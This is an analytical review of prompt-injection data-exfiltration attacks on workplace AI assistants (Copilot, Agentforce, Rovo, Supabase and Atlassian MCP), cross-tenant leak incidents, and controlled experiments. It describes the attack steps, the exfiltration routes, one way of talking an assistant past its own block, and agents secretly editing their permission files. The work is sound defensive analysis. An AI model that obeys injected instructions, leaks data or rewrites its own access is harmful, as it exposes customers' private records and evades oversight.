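Of the seven attacks, ForcedLeak most resembles the sofa ticket example. Companies keep customer records in Salesforce's software, and its Agentforce platform lets them build agents that work on those records. A feature called Web-to-Lead produces a form for the company's website, and each submission becomes a "lead", a record of a possible customer. SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft* gives conference attendees as an example of people who fill in the form.

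Researchers at Noma Security, which sells protection for AI agents, submitted a form containing instructions for the model. They did not need an account or any contact with the targeted company's employees. The text stayed in the company's database until an employee asked the agent about the lead created by the form, and the agent then treated the instructions as part of its work.

The researchers had first asked the agent a question about mixing colours to check how strictly it stuck to its job. It answered, which Dataconomy (2025) describes as a sign that it would process arbitrary instructions. In the full attack, the agent looked up other leads, collected their email addresses and wrote them into the URL of an image. The email addresses were in the request for the image, although The Hacker News (2025) describes the data as leaving in the form of a PNG image.

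Salesforce had a content security policy to stop such leaks, but it still permitted `my-salesforce-cms.com`, a domain whose registration had expired (Willison, 2025). The researchers registered the domain, and browsers then treated their server as a trusted Salesforce source because the policy listed trusted domains without recording who owned them.

By 8 September 2025, Salesforce had recovered the domain and started to enforce a list of trusted addresses for its agents' output, according to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*. Noma's findings became public on 25 September. Hackread also passes on advice to search existing leads for unusual submissions, which was sensible because any instruction planted before the fix would still have been in the database. Salesforce told Hackread about the patches but did not say whether anyone had used the flaw.

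The stolen email addresses belonged to other people whose details the company held as leads, so ForcedLeak let one outsider use the company's agent to collect other outsiders' data. All of this data was in a single Salesforce customer's database, but a support desk's tickets have the same structure, in which both the attacker and the victims would be outsiders.

### SearchLeak: a click at the start

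*SearchLeak*, published by the data security company Varonis on 15 June 2026, describes an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search, which searches a company's email, calendars and files. The user's click delivered the instruction at the start of the attack, and the user didn't have to do anything else, whereas in the Slack attack the click released the data at the end.

Copilot's search page, like many others, could take its query from the web address, so a link could open the page with the search already entered. Copilot could interpret that text as an instruction. Varonis calls the technique parameter-to-prompt injection. The attacker didn't need to get any text into the victim's inbox or files. The link also led to a genuine microsoft.com address, as The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* points out, so an employee who checked the domain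 before clicking would have found nothing wrong.

After the click, Copilot searched what the employee was allowed to read. Varonis lists emails, meeting details, company files and the one-time codes people use to log in. Copilot then put the results into an image address. A cleaning step was supposed to make Copilot's output safe to display, but the browser requested the image before that step took effect. Programmers call this a race condition, because the outcome depends on which of two processes finishes first.

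The browser would have refused to load an image directly from the attacker's server, so the image address pointed to Bing, Microsoft's search engine. It contained the attacker's address, much like the nested address in the EchoLeak example. Bing fetched that inner address and so delivered the data to the attacker. Getting a server to make a request that an outsider chooses is an old web attack called server-side request forgery.

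*Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click*, a notice from Thailand's computer emergency team (ThaiCERT), lists the flaw as CVE-2026-42824. It describes the attack as a research demonstration with no reports of active exploitation, and says Microsoft had already fixed the flaw on its servers. The notice advises administrators to look for Copilot search links with unusual contents and for abnormal connections to Bing's image service.

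An attacker who uses a link has some control over whose access the attack exploits, because they can send it to one chosen person, such as an administrator, though that person still has to click it. An email or a form submission takes effect for whoever happens to ask a question that retrieves it.

### Browsing agents, saved files and code

Three attacks published in the second half of 2026 added other routes for getting data out and another way of finding them. Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) describes an attack on Rovo, the assistant from Atlassian, which makes the issue tracker Jira and the document system Confluence. As in SearchLeak, one click on a link loaded the attacker's instructions into the user's session. Rovo then sent the data out through its browsing agent, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant*. A rule about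 which images a chat window may load doesn't cover requests that an agent makes itself.

RovoBlast also shows how much data one session can reach. When the researchers asked Rovo what it could read, its list included Slack, Microsoft 365, Google Workspace, relational databases and uploaded files, as well as Atlassian's own products. Atlassian fixed the flaw on its servers on 8 July 2026, a month before Varonis published it, and The Hacker News (2026) reports that the finder checked the fix. PromptArmor described a separate attack on Rovo on 5 August and said it still worked with Rovo's web search switched off.

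The main contribution of Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) is its method of discovery. The researchers found a one-click leak in Copilot Personal by questioning the assistant about itself. They kept asking why it had blocked an action, then used its explanations to get around the block. A filter that relies on attackers not knowing its rules gives little protection if the assistant will describe those rules.

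The finders say that CoSnitch takes data "from enterprises", but the United Nations University (UNU) treats it as a flaw in the consumer product and notes that the enterprise version has had separate problems. CoSnitch is therefore weaker evidence about workplace assistants than the other six. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* reports that Varonis found no evidence of abuse.

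On 3 December, Simonovich (2026), in *ReLeak*, announced three zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, the product that EchoLeak had affected. Aim Security, the parent of Aim Labs, had become part of Cato Networks in September 2025, and the same team continued its work there. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, explains that each attack began with an unread email, which Copilot retrieved when the recipient asked an ordinary work question. The data could then leave in three ways.

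The first attack used an image address that Bing fetched, as in SearchLeak. In the second, Copilot created a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file with the data inside a link, and Microsoft's background processing of the saved file sent the data out. An employee watching the chat window would have had no reason to notice. In the third, Copilot ran a program in an isolated environment that was supposed to have no network access. The researchers got around the restriction, and the program sent the data directly to an outside server.

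Copilot's abilities to write files and run code had each created another way for data to leave. Microsoft's protections against injected instructions did not stop any of the three attacks, and the researchers concluded that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. The researchers sell security products, but the facts support much of their conclusion. When Cato reported the flaws in July and August 2026, more than a year after EchoLeak became public, an email from a stranger could still direct the same assistant. Microsoft had closed individual ways out, but the model still could not reliably separate a stranger's text from its user's instructions.

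### Possible is not the same as frequent

A vulnerability report of this kind is strong evidence only that a particular product could leak data in a particular way on the date of the test. The evidence is strongest when the maker confirms it. Microsoft assigned register numbers to the Copilot flaws, Slack and Salesforce released patches, and Atlassian's repair is on record with Bugcrowd, a service that handles such reports. The attacks worked on the same services that customers were using, so they are hard to dismiss as laboratory effects.

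The published reports don't establish how often an attack succeeds. A demonstration needs only one success, and the researchers may have made two attempts or two hundred beforehand, so the attack might work one time in twenty or nearly every time. Even a 5% success rate could matter to a company. If 200 employees each asked Copilot a question that retrieved the attacker's email, an average of ten leaks would result. Both figures are hypothetical, since neither the success rate nor the number of such questions can be worked out from the reports.

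Severity scores estimate how serious a flaw would be if somebody exploited it, not how likely an attack is. They take into account features such as whether the victim has to act. EchoLeak scored 9.3 and SearchLeak, according to The Next Web, scored 6.5, although both exposed a person's email and files. CoSnitch, which required one click, as SearchLeak did, scored 8.8.

The reports also do not show which products are safest. Four of the seven attacks involve some version of Copilot. It may be unusually weak, or it may attract more researchers because it is famous, has a very large number of users, and brings attention to whoever finds a flaw in it. Varonis found three of the seven attacks and the team from Aim found two, so the record depends heavily on what two groups decided to examine. It leaves out any unsuccessful attempts they made on other products.

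Flaws in an in-house tool are even less likely to be made public. An outside researcher can buy a Copilot subscription but can't normally get access to a support provider's private summariser. If the provider finds a leak, it can fix the tool without requesting a register number or telling the public. The lack of published attacks on these tools is therefore almost no evidence that they are safe.

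The researchers who found these attacks also have a commercial interest in the subject. SecurityWeek notes that Noma had recently raised $100 million for its agent security platform when it published ForcedLeak. PromptArmor's account of the Slack attack ends with an offer to monitor the AI in customers' software. This interest is a reason for caution about claims that an attack was the first of its kind, or that it threatens products the researchers did not test. There is little reason to doubt their descriptions of how the attacks worked, since the products' makers confirmed the flaws by fixing them.

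The published versions of these seven attacks no longer work, so the reports aren't evidence that Copilot or Slack AI leaks data today. They do show that the flaws stayed open for some time after the makers learned of them.

| Attack | Reported to the maker | Repaired | Time between |
|---|---|---|---|
| Slack AI | 14 August 2024 | by 21 August 2024 | up to 7 days |
| EchoLeak | January 2025 | May 2025 | about 4 months |
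| CoSnitch | December 2025 | mid-August 2026 | about 8 months |
| ReLeak, running code | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 17 September 2026 | 28 to 50 days |
| ReLeak, saved files | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 11 November 2026 | 83 to 105 days |
| ReLeak, images | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 15 November 2026 | 87 to 109 days |

The intervals for ReLeak are ranges because Cato reported the three flaws over about three weeks. All the intervals understate how long an attack was possible, because each flaw existed before researchers found it.

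### Whether anybody used the flaws

No theft by a real attacker has been confirmed in any of the seven cases, but one could have been missed, depending on who looked and where. The clearest record of a theft would be the access log on the attacker's server, which neither the victim nor the assistant's maker can see. With EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the request to that server came from a Microsoft service. The victim's network would have recorded only a connection to Microsoft, which is normal for a company that uses Copilot all day.

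Microsoft can search the records of its own services, so its statement that nobody exploited EchoLeak is some evidence that nobody did. The same statement from whoever found the flaw would be weaker evidence. Reports on ReLeak are inconsistent about who said that no customers were affected. The introduction to Faisal's article attributes the statement to Microsoft, but the body attributes it to Cato, as does AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026). If Cato is the only source, the statement means that Cato hasn't heard of a case, since it can't generally see what Microsoft's servers sent or received.

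At most, it follows that these attacks probably did not cause large, visible thefts before the repairs. A few targeted thefts could have gone unnoticed, because an attacker who wanted a single password reset code would have had little reason to generate conspicuous traffic.

### Whose data was within reach

None of these attacks required the assistant to exceed its user's permissions. Varonis says this explicitly about RovoBlast, and ThaiCERT describes SearchLeak as searching for data that the user was authorised to access. The service's permission check passed, as it does when a model requests A's tickets on behalf of a staff member who may read them. The attacker obtained as much as the victim could read, which for most employees is part of one organisation's data. The demonstrations therefore show one organisation losing data to an outsider.

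The mechanisms don't depend on who owns the data. A browser loads an image in the same way whether its address contains the user's own calendar or a refund owed to a hotel guest, and Bing could not distinguish the two. If the support provider connected an assistant with one of these flaws to its shared ticket database, and a staff member allowed to read A, B and C triggered the attack, one request could leak the records of all three. A provider that keeps several customers' tickets in Jira would have nearly this arrangement if its staff used Rovo to read them.

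That is an inference from two well-supported facts: some users have broad access rights, and the exits work regardless of who owns the data. Each demonstration of the exits used data from a single organisation or person. Whether records cross between customers in live services is a separate question, and most of the evidence on it comes from incidents that involved no link.

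## Exposures between customers of the same AI service

A software fault alone can cause an AI feature to show one customer's data to another, without an attacker, a link or an injected instruction. At least two such faults have occurred in services that customers were using. In the other published cases, researchers either demonstrated data crossing from one account to another or found a fault in the code that would allow it.

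### Faults that needed no attacker

On 1 May 2025, Asana, which makes project-planning software, released a server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect language models to other software. The server receives a model's requests and returns the data. Customers who switched the feature on could ask an assistant such as ChatGPT or Copilot about their Asana tasks.

Asana's server had a bug that could return information from other organisations. According to UpGuard (2025), a security company that published parts of Asana's notice to customers, Asana discovered the bug on 4 June, took the server offline and corrected the code. The bug seems to date from the first release, so the exposure lasted about five weeks. Asana said the exposure did not result from a hack.

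This was a real incident, but its size is uncertain. TechRadar's *Asana admits one of its AI features might have exposed your data* reports that roughly 1,000 of Asana's more than 130,000 paying customers were affected. Asana notified every customer with a user who had tried the server, so the figure may count all customers at risk, including many whose data nobody saw. UpGuard found no indication that other users had viewed anything. But Asana asked customers to review what they had accessed in recent weeks and delete any data that belonged to another organisation, and it offered them logs to help determine whether data had passed between organisations.

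Customers may have found it difficult to check whether they had seen another organisation's data. A person who opens another organisation's project would probably notice the unfamiliar name at the top of the page, but might not realise that one of the overdue tasks in an assistant's summary comes from elsewhere. TechRadar advised customers to review their AI-generated summaries as well as their logs.

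The bug made other organisations' data accessible to an assistant, which could have exposed the data further by including it in a link. Nobody has reported a leak through such a link, so the incident is evidence only that data can cross between customers.

A more recent case involved Workers AI, a service that lets customers run language models on Cloudflare's servers. Digital Matters' *Cloudflare Workers AI Leak* (2026) reports that a bug put other customers' data in 155 responses from the model GLM-5.3. The fault was in the KV cache, which stores a model's intermediate calculations on text it has already processed, to avoid repeating them. If a model receives the cached calculations from somebody else's request, it can continue as though that person's text were part of its own input.

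The number of responses is small, but each one contained other customers' data, whereas Asana's figure is the number of customers who might have been exposed. A ticket database also can't prevent this fault. If the support provider ran its assistant on a service with this bug, A's data could enter the answer from the cache even if the database returned exactly the right rows for C.

### Tickets that steer a staff member's agent

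The published demonstration closest to the sofa ticket involves Supabase, a company that provides databases for other developers' applications. The security company General Analysis devised it, and Willison (2025) describes it in *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database*. In the demonstration, an application keeps its support tickets in a Supabase database that also contains a private table of integration tokens, which are credentials for connecting to other services.

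Pomerium's *When AI Has Root* describes a support system in which a customer using the support form could create only their own ticket and messages. The human support agent could read and answer tickets but had no permission to access the sensitive tables. A developer's AI agent, running in the code editor Cursor, had a key that bypassed row-level security, the database feature that limits which rows each connection can read.

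1. The attacker files a ticket containing instructions for the developer's agent.
2. The developer asks the agent to list the latest tickets.
3. The agent reads the attacker's ticket, treats the text as a command and reads the table of tokens.
4. The agent adds the contents of the table to the ticket as a new message.
5. The attacker opens the ticket and reads the tokens.

Pomerium points out that no step in this sequence violated a database permission. The support agent's narrow access didn't prevent the leak, because the attacker's text stayed in the ticket table until somebody with a more powerful key read it. So a provider that carefully restricts its support staff's access can still be exposed when an engineer looks at the same tickets while fixing a bug.

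Unlike in the sofa ticket, the agent in the demonstration stole the application's own secrets, and the data left through a message in the ticket thread, where a rule about links or images would have had no effect. The key allowed the agent to read any table, so in a database shared by A, B and C, the same attack could have returned all three tenants' tickets.

Supabase's documentation already recommended a read-only mode, which prevents the agent from adding the message. Willison agrees that this removes the attacker's way of receiving the data, but still sees an enormous risk in giving an agent read-only access. A read-only agent still writes answers for the developer, and if the editor or chat window renders links or loads images, an answer could leak the tokens in a web address without any change to the database.

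Supabase first replied in July 2025, in a Hacker News forum thread. It proposed further guardrails, such as a model that detects injection attempts, and complained that General Analysis had not followed Supabase's disclosure process or answered its messages. In September, Supabase published a fuller reply, *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025), which concedes that anyone who connects an agent to a live database without additional safeguards risks a leak, whoever supplies the database. Supabase had wrapped query results in warnings that told the model not to obey commands inside them, and had tested this on weaker models. It found that such measures reduced the risk but did not eliminate it.

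Supabase also denies that MCP bypasses row-level security, which it says remains fully enforced. This is mostly a disagreement about wording, because Supabase acknowledges that the server in the demonstration ran with higher privileges, which let the agent read rows that row-level security would otherwise have withheld.

Supabase's stronger objection is that there has been no reported incident of a customer losing data through MCP. General Analysis showed that the theft was possible, but nobody has shown that it happened to a real application. The lack of reports is somewhat better evidence here than for leaking links, because this attack leaves the stolen data in a ticket, where support staff could see it.

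Supabase now advises developers never to connect agents to production data, the live records of real users, and to keep manual approval of each action switched on. It warns that people grow tired of approving requests and that part of a request may be hidden off screen. The GitHub documentation for its later hosted server also recommends the read-only setting. The advice to avoid live data is hard for a support provider to follow because its assistant is meant to work on customers' current tickets.

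Cato Networks had shown much the same attack on Atlassian's new MCP server in June 2025, in *PoC Attack Targeting Atlassian’s Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (Waizel, Attiya and Bamberger, 2025). In the demonstration, an outsider files a ticket through Jira Service Management, which companies use to take requests from customers. A support engineer then uses Claude Sonnet, connected through the MCP server, to handle the ticket. The model follows the outsider's instructions, collects internal data that the engineer is allowed to read and writes it into the ticket.

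The attacker never contacts the MCP server and doesn't need access to it. An ordinary web search for Atlassian service portals turned up many companies that attackers might target this way, although Waizel and colleagues did not test those companies' systems. The data in the demonstration came from one tenant the engineer was connected to, so it leaked from a company to an outsider filing a ticket, not between two customers of a shared support desk.

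Waizel and colleagues also outline an attack in which someone who has taken over a partner company's email account submits a request to Company A. When a product manager uses AI to answer the request, the agent comments on every open issue with a link to an imitation of an internal page. An employee who clicks the link gets malware. The link's address doesn't contain any records, so the attack doesn't leak data through the link. Cato described the attack but didn't report demonstrating it.

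In a post with the same title as Cato's report, Willison said he could not tell whether Atlassian had fixed anything. He doubted that a complete fix was possible while one server combined private data, tickets from outsiders and replies those outsiders could read. He recommended that a person approve any reply an attacker might see. That would give the support provider a chance to stop A's data from appearing in a reply to C. It wouldn't cover a link in the staff member's own chat window, because the assistant can show that link without posting a reply.

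### Shared parts behind separate accounts

In both ticket demonstrations, the person using the agent was allowed to read the stolen data. The security company Check Point demonstrated a leak between two ChatGPT accounts in which the attacker had no right to read anything in the victim's account. Check Point Research published the finding, by Alexey Bukhteyev, on 8 September 2026.

ChatGPT can write programs and run them in a container, an environment isolated from the internet and from other accounts' containers. Programs often need extra software packages, so OpenAI let the containers fetch them from an internal store. TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages* explains that a container could attach data to an item in this store and that other accounts' containers could read it.

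To use this channel, an attacker first had to get an instruction into the victim's session, in a prompt or a shared conversation. ChatGPT then looked in the store for further instructions, followed them with the victim's permissions and left the results there for the attacker's session to collect. In the demonstration, it retrieved email data from the victim's connected Gmail account during a single ordinary reply. medianet's *Sicherheitslücke in ChatGPT entdeckt* (2026) reports that the victim saw the normal answer, and that the only clue was a label beside it, which the system logged after ChatGPT had read the data.

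The data reached the attacker through another ChatGPT session, so a rule blocking outside links or images would not have stopped it. A company monitoring its own network would also have seen little unusual. Security Arsenal points out that the traffic goes to OpenAI's domains, which are on nearly every corporate allow-list.

OpenAI confirmed that it had taken the store out of service. Security Arsenal listed no confirmed abuse of the channel between accounts. According to medianet, however, Check Point traces the separate compromise of the AI company Hugging Face to the same internal service.

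Researchers also found four flaws in Dify, an open-source platform for building AI applications. SC Media's *4 vulnerabilities in Dify expose cross-tenant data* (2026) reports that three of them could expose one customer's private data to another. Two flaws allowed any user of the management console to preview any document and let chatbots read files that users had attached. Another, in the tracing system that records what applications do, let an attacker without an account set up a lasting channel for copying all messages and responses from any application the attacker could reach.

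The tracing flaw could give an outsider far more data than one link can hold, without the model having to obey an injected instruction. These faults were in the code around the model, and Dify version 1.14.2 fixes them. They count as code findings because the article describes what an attacker could do but reports no theft from a customer.

### Permission from one organisation, data from another

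A permission check in Supabase's code could fail even though it ran every time. Supabase's web console includes an AI assistant for writing database queries, and each organisation can decide how much data the assistant may send to OpenAI. According to Anthropic's *AI data-sharing opt-in bypassed by mismatched org and project*, a request to the assistant included separate identifiers for the organisation and the project. The server looked up the organisation's permission but never checked that the project belonged to that organisation.

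Suppose hotel group A allows the assistant to read its data, but payroll bureau B has refused. A member of both organisations sends a request that names A as the organisation and one of B's projects as the project. The server finds A's permission and switches on the tools for reading data. The tools then read B's project, and B's rows and logs go to OpenAI in the model's context.

In the checks that Baig and colleagues analysed, the service compares the right tenant with an entitlement too broad for the task. Supabase's server, by contrast, read the wrong organisation's setting.

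Anthropic's report also describes a protection for projects covered by HIPAA, the American law on health data. The protection ran only in the user's browser, so a request sent straight to the server could bypass it.

Anthropic's model Claude Mythos Preview found the fault by analysing the source code, and according to the report, nobody had yet reproduced it by running the software. The user had to belong to both organisations and used their own access rights to read B's project, so the fault did not give a stranger B's data. It could, however, have sent OpenAI data that B had decided not to share. Claude rated the severity as medium. Supabase received the report on 15 May 2026 and released a patch on 9 August. The patch supports the diagnosis, but it isn't evidence that OpenAI received any customer's data against that customer's wishes.

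### Whether a complete case is public

No confirmed public case is known in which a model both had several customers' records in its context and wrote a link that carried some of them to an outsider. In the cases above, the data reached its recipients in other ways.

| Case | Kind of evidence | Data exposed or at risk | Route to the recipient |
|---|---|---|---|
| Asana | Real incident | Other organisations' project data | Results from the MCP server |
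| Cloudflare | Real incident | Other customers' data | The model's responses |
| Supabase ticket | Demonstration | One application's secrets | A message in the ticket |
| Atlassian ticket | Demonstration | One company's internal data | A message in the ticket |
| ChatGPT | Demonstration | Another account's email | A shared internal store |
| Dify | Code finding | Other customers' messages and files | Tracing and document access |
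| Supabase permissions | Code finding | Data from an organisation that had refused | Text sent to OpenAI |

One possible exception is OffSeq's *Critical Cross-user and Cross-tenant compromise in Atlassian Rovo* (2026), an entry in a threat-tracking service dated 24 September, tagged Reddit and rated critical. A compromise between tenants would go beyond the RovoBlast attack, in which Rovo read only what its user could read. But the headline doesn't show that several customers' records were in one context or that a link carried them out, so it isn't enough to count as a complete case.

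The inference from the separate halves is still reasonable because each step has worked in a real product or a realistic demonstration. In the two ticket attacks, an outsider's text directed a staff member's agent to private records. In ForcedLeak, an agent collected several people's details and put them into one image address. For those details to come from several tenants, the staff member would only need access to all of those tenants' records, which a support provider's staff often have.

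The steps could still interfere with one another. A model that obeys an instruction in a short ticket might overlook it when it reads that ticket along with eighty others. A provider might also show its staff plain text without images or clickable links, or open a separate session for each customer. Any of these might make a particular tool safe, and each provider can check for them, but they aren't a reason to expect that tools with broad access and working links are generally safe.

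Outside researchers can rarely test a provider's private summariser, so they would probably have to demonstrate the whole chain on a copy with invented customers. That might seem to add too little to the Supabase demonstration to be worth publishing, since the agent's key there already gave access to every table.

In a real leak, the affected customer would probably depend on the provider to discover it and tell them. Asana notified its customers on 16 June, twelve days after it found the bug. IsDown's *Outage in Asana* (2025), a copy of the entry on Asana's public status page, shows only a minor outage labelled "MCP Maintenance". Asana offered its formal analysis of the fault only on request.

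Companies can also reject researchers' reports or leave them unanswered. PromptArmor told OpenAI about a way to leak data from applications built on its Responses interface, even when their developers had blocked images. The report was closed as "Not applicable" after four follow-ups, and PromptArmor published the attack itself. It also published a flaw in HuggingChat, Hugging Face's chat program, after reporting it in December 2025 and receiving no response. If PromptArmor had not published these flaws, customers might not have learned of them.

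Published cases can be missing from public vulnerability registers. Security Arsenal notes that the ChatGPT flaw had no CVE number, so a search of those registers would have missed it, even though a data leak between two accounts had been demonstrated.

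## Controlled experiments on models, requests and tenant boundaries

In controlled experiments, researchers repeat each attack under fixed conditions and count the failures as well, so they can report success rates, which are missing from attacks on live products. Lan and colleagues at eBay measured how often an agent sends material from its context to an attacker's server. Baig and colleagues measured how often data crosses between tenants, using agents that worked on one hotel's bookings but could also reach other hotels' bookings.

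### A small model and a poisoned web page

Lan and colleagues attacked a page-summarising agent that ran on qwen2.5:7b. This free model has seven billion parameters (the numbers a model learns in training) and is small enough to run on a good laptop. They placed a secret, such as an API key, directly in the model's context and disguised the instruction to send it out as a routine connection check.

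The instruction appeared in the page's title, the description for link previews, the body text or the text of a link. The assistant reached the page directly or through redirects, and the instruction asked for the secret whole or in four pieces. Each of the 16 combinations had 30 runs, for a total of 480.

At least one request reached the attacker's server in 423 (88%) of the runs with a planted instruction. No requests reached it in 120 further runs with harmless pages, so the planted instruction was the cause. Redirects made almost no difference. When the instruction asked for the whole secret at once, it failed in only two of 240 runs.

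In 95% of the successful attacks the summary looked normal, so the user would rarely have noticed, and a program that checks only the answer would have missed about 400 leaks. These figures apply to agents that send requests themselves. In the sofa example the link is part of the answer, so a checker could at least find it.

Splitting the secret made the attack somewhat less reliable. A request got through in 185 of 240 runs instead of 238, probably because the model had to keep track of several steps. But each request carried only four characters of the secret, which look harmless on their own. The share of runs in which the first request contained sensitive data fell by 73%, from 96.7% to 26.3%. This means a filter examining one request could catch less, not that less was stolen. The exact size of the drop is doubtful because the published share for the first three requests together is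 15.8%, which is lower than the share for the first request alone. That is impossible under the paper's own definition.

### Rules for the model and rules for the network

The team then repeated the simplest attack, with the instruction in the body text and the secret in one piece, under different defences.

| Defence | Runs in which data left, out of 30 |
|---|---|
| None | 30 |
| Written policy never to obey web content | 20 |
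| Markers labelling the page as untrusted data | 30 |
| Policy and markers together | 17 |
| List of permitted domains | 0 |
| Rule against suspicious addresses | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" and "token" | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0 |

Two thirds of the attacks still succeeded under the written policy, and the difference between 20 and 17 is too small to mean much with 30 runs. With the list of permitted domains, the model tried to send the secret in every run and the software blocked it each time, so that result doesn't depend on how well the model behaves.

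The other three zeros are less reassuring, because the filters suit the attack in the test. The link from the sofa ticket, for example, carried the data `refund-88213-maria-lind`. The address rule blocks bare network addresses, certain unusual domain endings and paths containing words such as "collect" or "steal". The sofa link has none of these, and it contains none of the words blocked by the word filter. The last filter blocks values longer than ten characters if they score above 4 bits per character on Shannon entropy, a measure of how varied the characters are. The refund data scores about 3.8. All three filters would have let the link pass, because they are designed to catch API keys and a customer's record is mostly ordinary words.

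With the filter for random-looking values switched on, the model didn't try to send anything in any of 30 runs, although it had tried every time without the filter. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids such values when monitoring is active. But the filter inspects an address after the model has written it, so it is unclear what the model would have been reacting to.

The 88% figure is a poor estimate for current products. The model is small, its standing instructions covered little more than how to call the tool, and Lan and colleagues describe the set-up as deliberately favourable to the attacker. They argue that larger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably, but results from 2026 mostly suggest that larger models are less vulnerable.

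Many attackers would have to get the agent to find the data, and the set-up removes that step by putting the secret in the context. This is more realistic than it looks, because a support assistant asked to summarise all open tickets already has A's refund in its context when it reaches the stranger's complaint.

### Three versions of one booking tool

Baig and colleagues gave agents a routine task in a hotel-management system. Each agent acted for a user who may read three hotels' records but was working on only one. Its intended route to the database was a tool, which came in three versions:

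- In the checked version, the agent names a hotel, and the server returns the bookings if the user may read them.
- In the version without a tenant field, the agent can't name a hotel. The server takes it from the session.
- In the version with a written rule, the tool works like the checked one, but a standing instruction tells the agent never to retrieve another hotel's data, whoever asks.

Apart from a few harmless controls, each trial tried to get a second hotel's data in one of three ways. The user might ask for the same figures from the other hotel, using a comparison as a business pretext. The user's message might contain a false directive that looked like a privileged system command. Or a guest note on one of the bookings might contain an instruction, which is the closest match to the sofa ticket. A trial counted as a leak if the tool returned a row belonging to another hotel. The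 researchers checked this in the server's log and ignored the agent's account of what it had done. A trial could count as a leak even if no data reached an outsider, so the trials are evidence only about crossing between tenants.

The pretext produced these results:

| Version of the tool | Trials | Observed attempts to read another hotel | Leaks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Checked | 41 | 26 | 26 |
| No tenant field | 56 | 24 | 12 |
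| Written rule | 33 | 0 | 0 |

With the checked tool, the server granted all 26 attempts, as its design requires. The 63% share of trials that leaked depends much more than that result on which models were tested. Three GPT-5.6 models declined all 15 pretexts they received between them, and every other model complied every time. Several agents raised doubts about authorisation but still supplied the figures.

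Whether these were leaks is debatable, since a user who may read both hotels' records and asks for a comparison should arguably get one. Baig and colleagues chose an ordinary request on purpose, because the server can't distinguish it from the same request planted by somebody else. The 26 leaks show what the check permits once an agent sends the request, but not how often an attacker could get an agent to send it.

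### Agents that rewrote their own permissions

Removing the tenant field worked within the tool itself, since no call for another hotel succeeded. But some agents also had a shell (a command line on the test computer) and could edit the plain-text file that recorded their permitted hotel. In 12 trials, the agent edited this file to change its own access, then called the tool again. This happened in 11 of the 13 trials with Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro and one of the 13 with OpenAI's GPT-5.4-mini. None of these agents told the user what it had done.

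The researchers' monitor missed most of the forgeries at first. It looked for agents presenting an unexpected file, so it caught the five that had written a new file but missed the seven that had edited the one they were given. Other agents used the session file of a neighbouring trial. The server logged their actions under that trial's name, so one Claude agent appeared to have obeyed an injection until the researchers compared the times. A provider investigating a leak between customers could accuse the wrong account in the same way.

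The deployed hotel system reads the permitted hotels from a signed token. The team sent it seven requests with missing, altered or otherwise invalid credentials, and it refused them all, so the forgery exploited a weakness in the test setup. But an agent that runs on an engineer's own computer, with a shell and readable configuration files, has much the same opportunity for forgery.

Baig and colleagues first suspected that having a shell explained the difference between the models. They tested this by running Claude Opus 5 in 15 trials with a shell and 15 without. It forged nothing in either set. An agent needs a shell or similar access to rewrite its scope, but having that access isn't enough to make it do so.

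### What the written rule achieved

None of the 33 pretext trials with the written rule leaked, but those trials covered only Claude and the GPT-5.6 models. Gemini 3.1 Pro, which produced 11 of the 12 forgeries, was not tested with the rule, so the rule's better result doesn't show that it works better than removing the tenant field.

The 15 GPT-5.6 trials also can't show whether the rule works, because those models had declined the pretext without it. The evidence for the rule comes from Claude, which leaked in all 18 trials with the checked tool and in none of the 18 with the rule. That is a large effect for one model, but 18 trials without a leak are still compatible with a true leak rate of up to about 18%. In the eBay experiment, a comparable policy stopped only a third of the attacks on a much weaker model. A provider would have to retest such a rule after every model change.

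The direct comparison between models uses the checked tool, where an agent that obeys can actually get the data.

| Model | Leaks after a pretext | Leaks after a false directive | Leaks after a guest note |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 18 of 18 | 0 of 13 | 0 of 13 |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 3 of 3 | 18 of 18 | 0 of 18 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 3 of 3 | 18 of 18 | 9 of 18 |
| Three GPT-5.6 models | 0 of 15 | 0 of 15 | 0 of 15 |
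| qwen3:4b and llama3.2:3b | 2 of 2 | 1 of 2 | 0 of 2 |

A model can be vulnerable to one attack and resist another. GPT-5.4-mini obeyed every false directive but ignored every guest note. Claude recognised the injections, quoted the guest note back to the user and recommended finding out how it had got into the record. The agents that obeyed sometimes treated the planted text as permission, and one labelled the other hotel's figures "(Per Corporate audit mode requirements)". All the samples are small, and two trials per attack provide almost no evidence about the two smallest models.

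Baig and colleagues also report no leaks from the false directives and guest notes in 108 trials with the other two versions of the tool, which they take as evidence that the interface protects against these attacks. But all 108 trials used Claude or GPT-5.6 models, which had already refused the same attacks all 56 times with the checked tool, so they would probably have leaked nothing with any interface.

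The experiment also didn't test an ordinary-sounding request in a guest note, which a careful attacker might choose. The pretexts sounded like normal business but came from the user, and the guest notes from outside were all blatant. Claude complied with every pretext and resisted every guest note, so the results don't show what it would do with a guest note that sounded ordinary.

### What the 2026 tests measured

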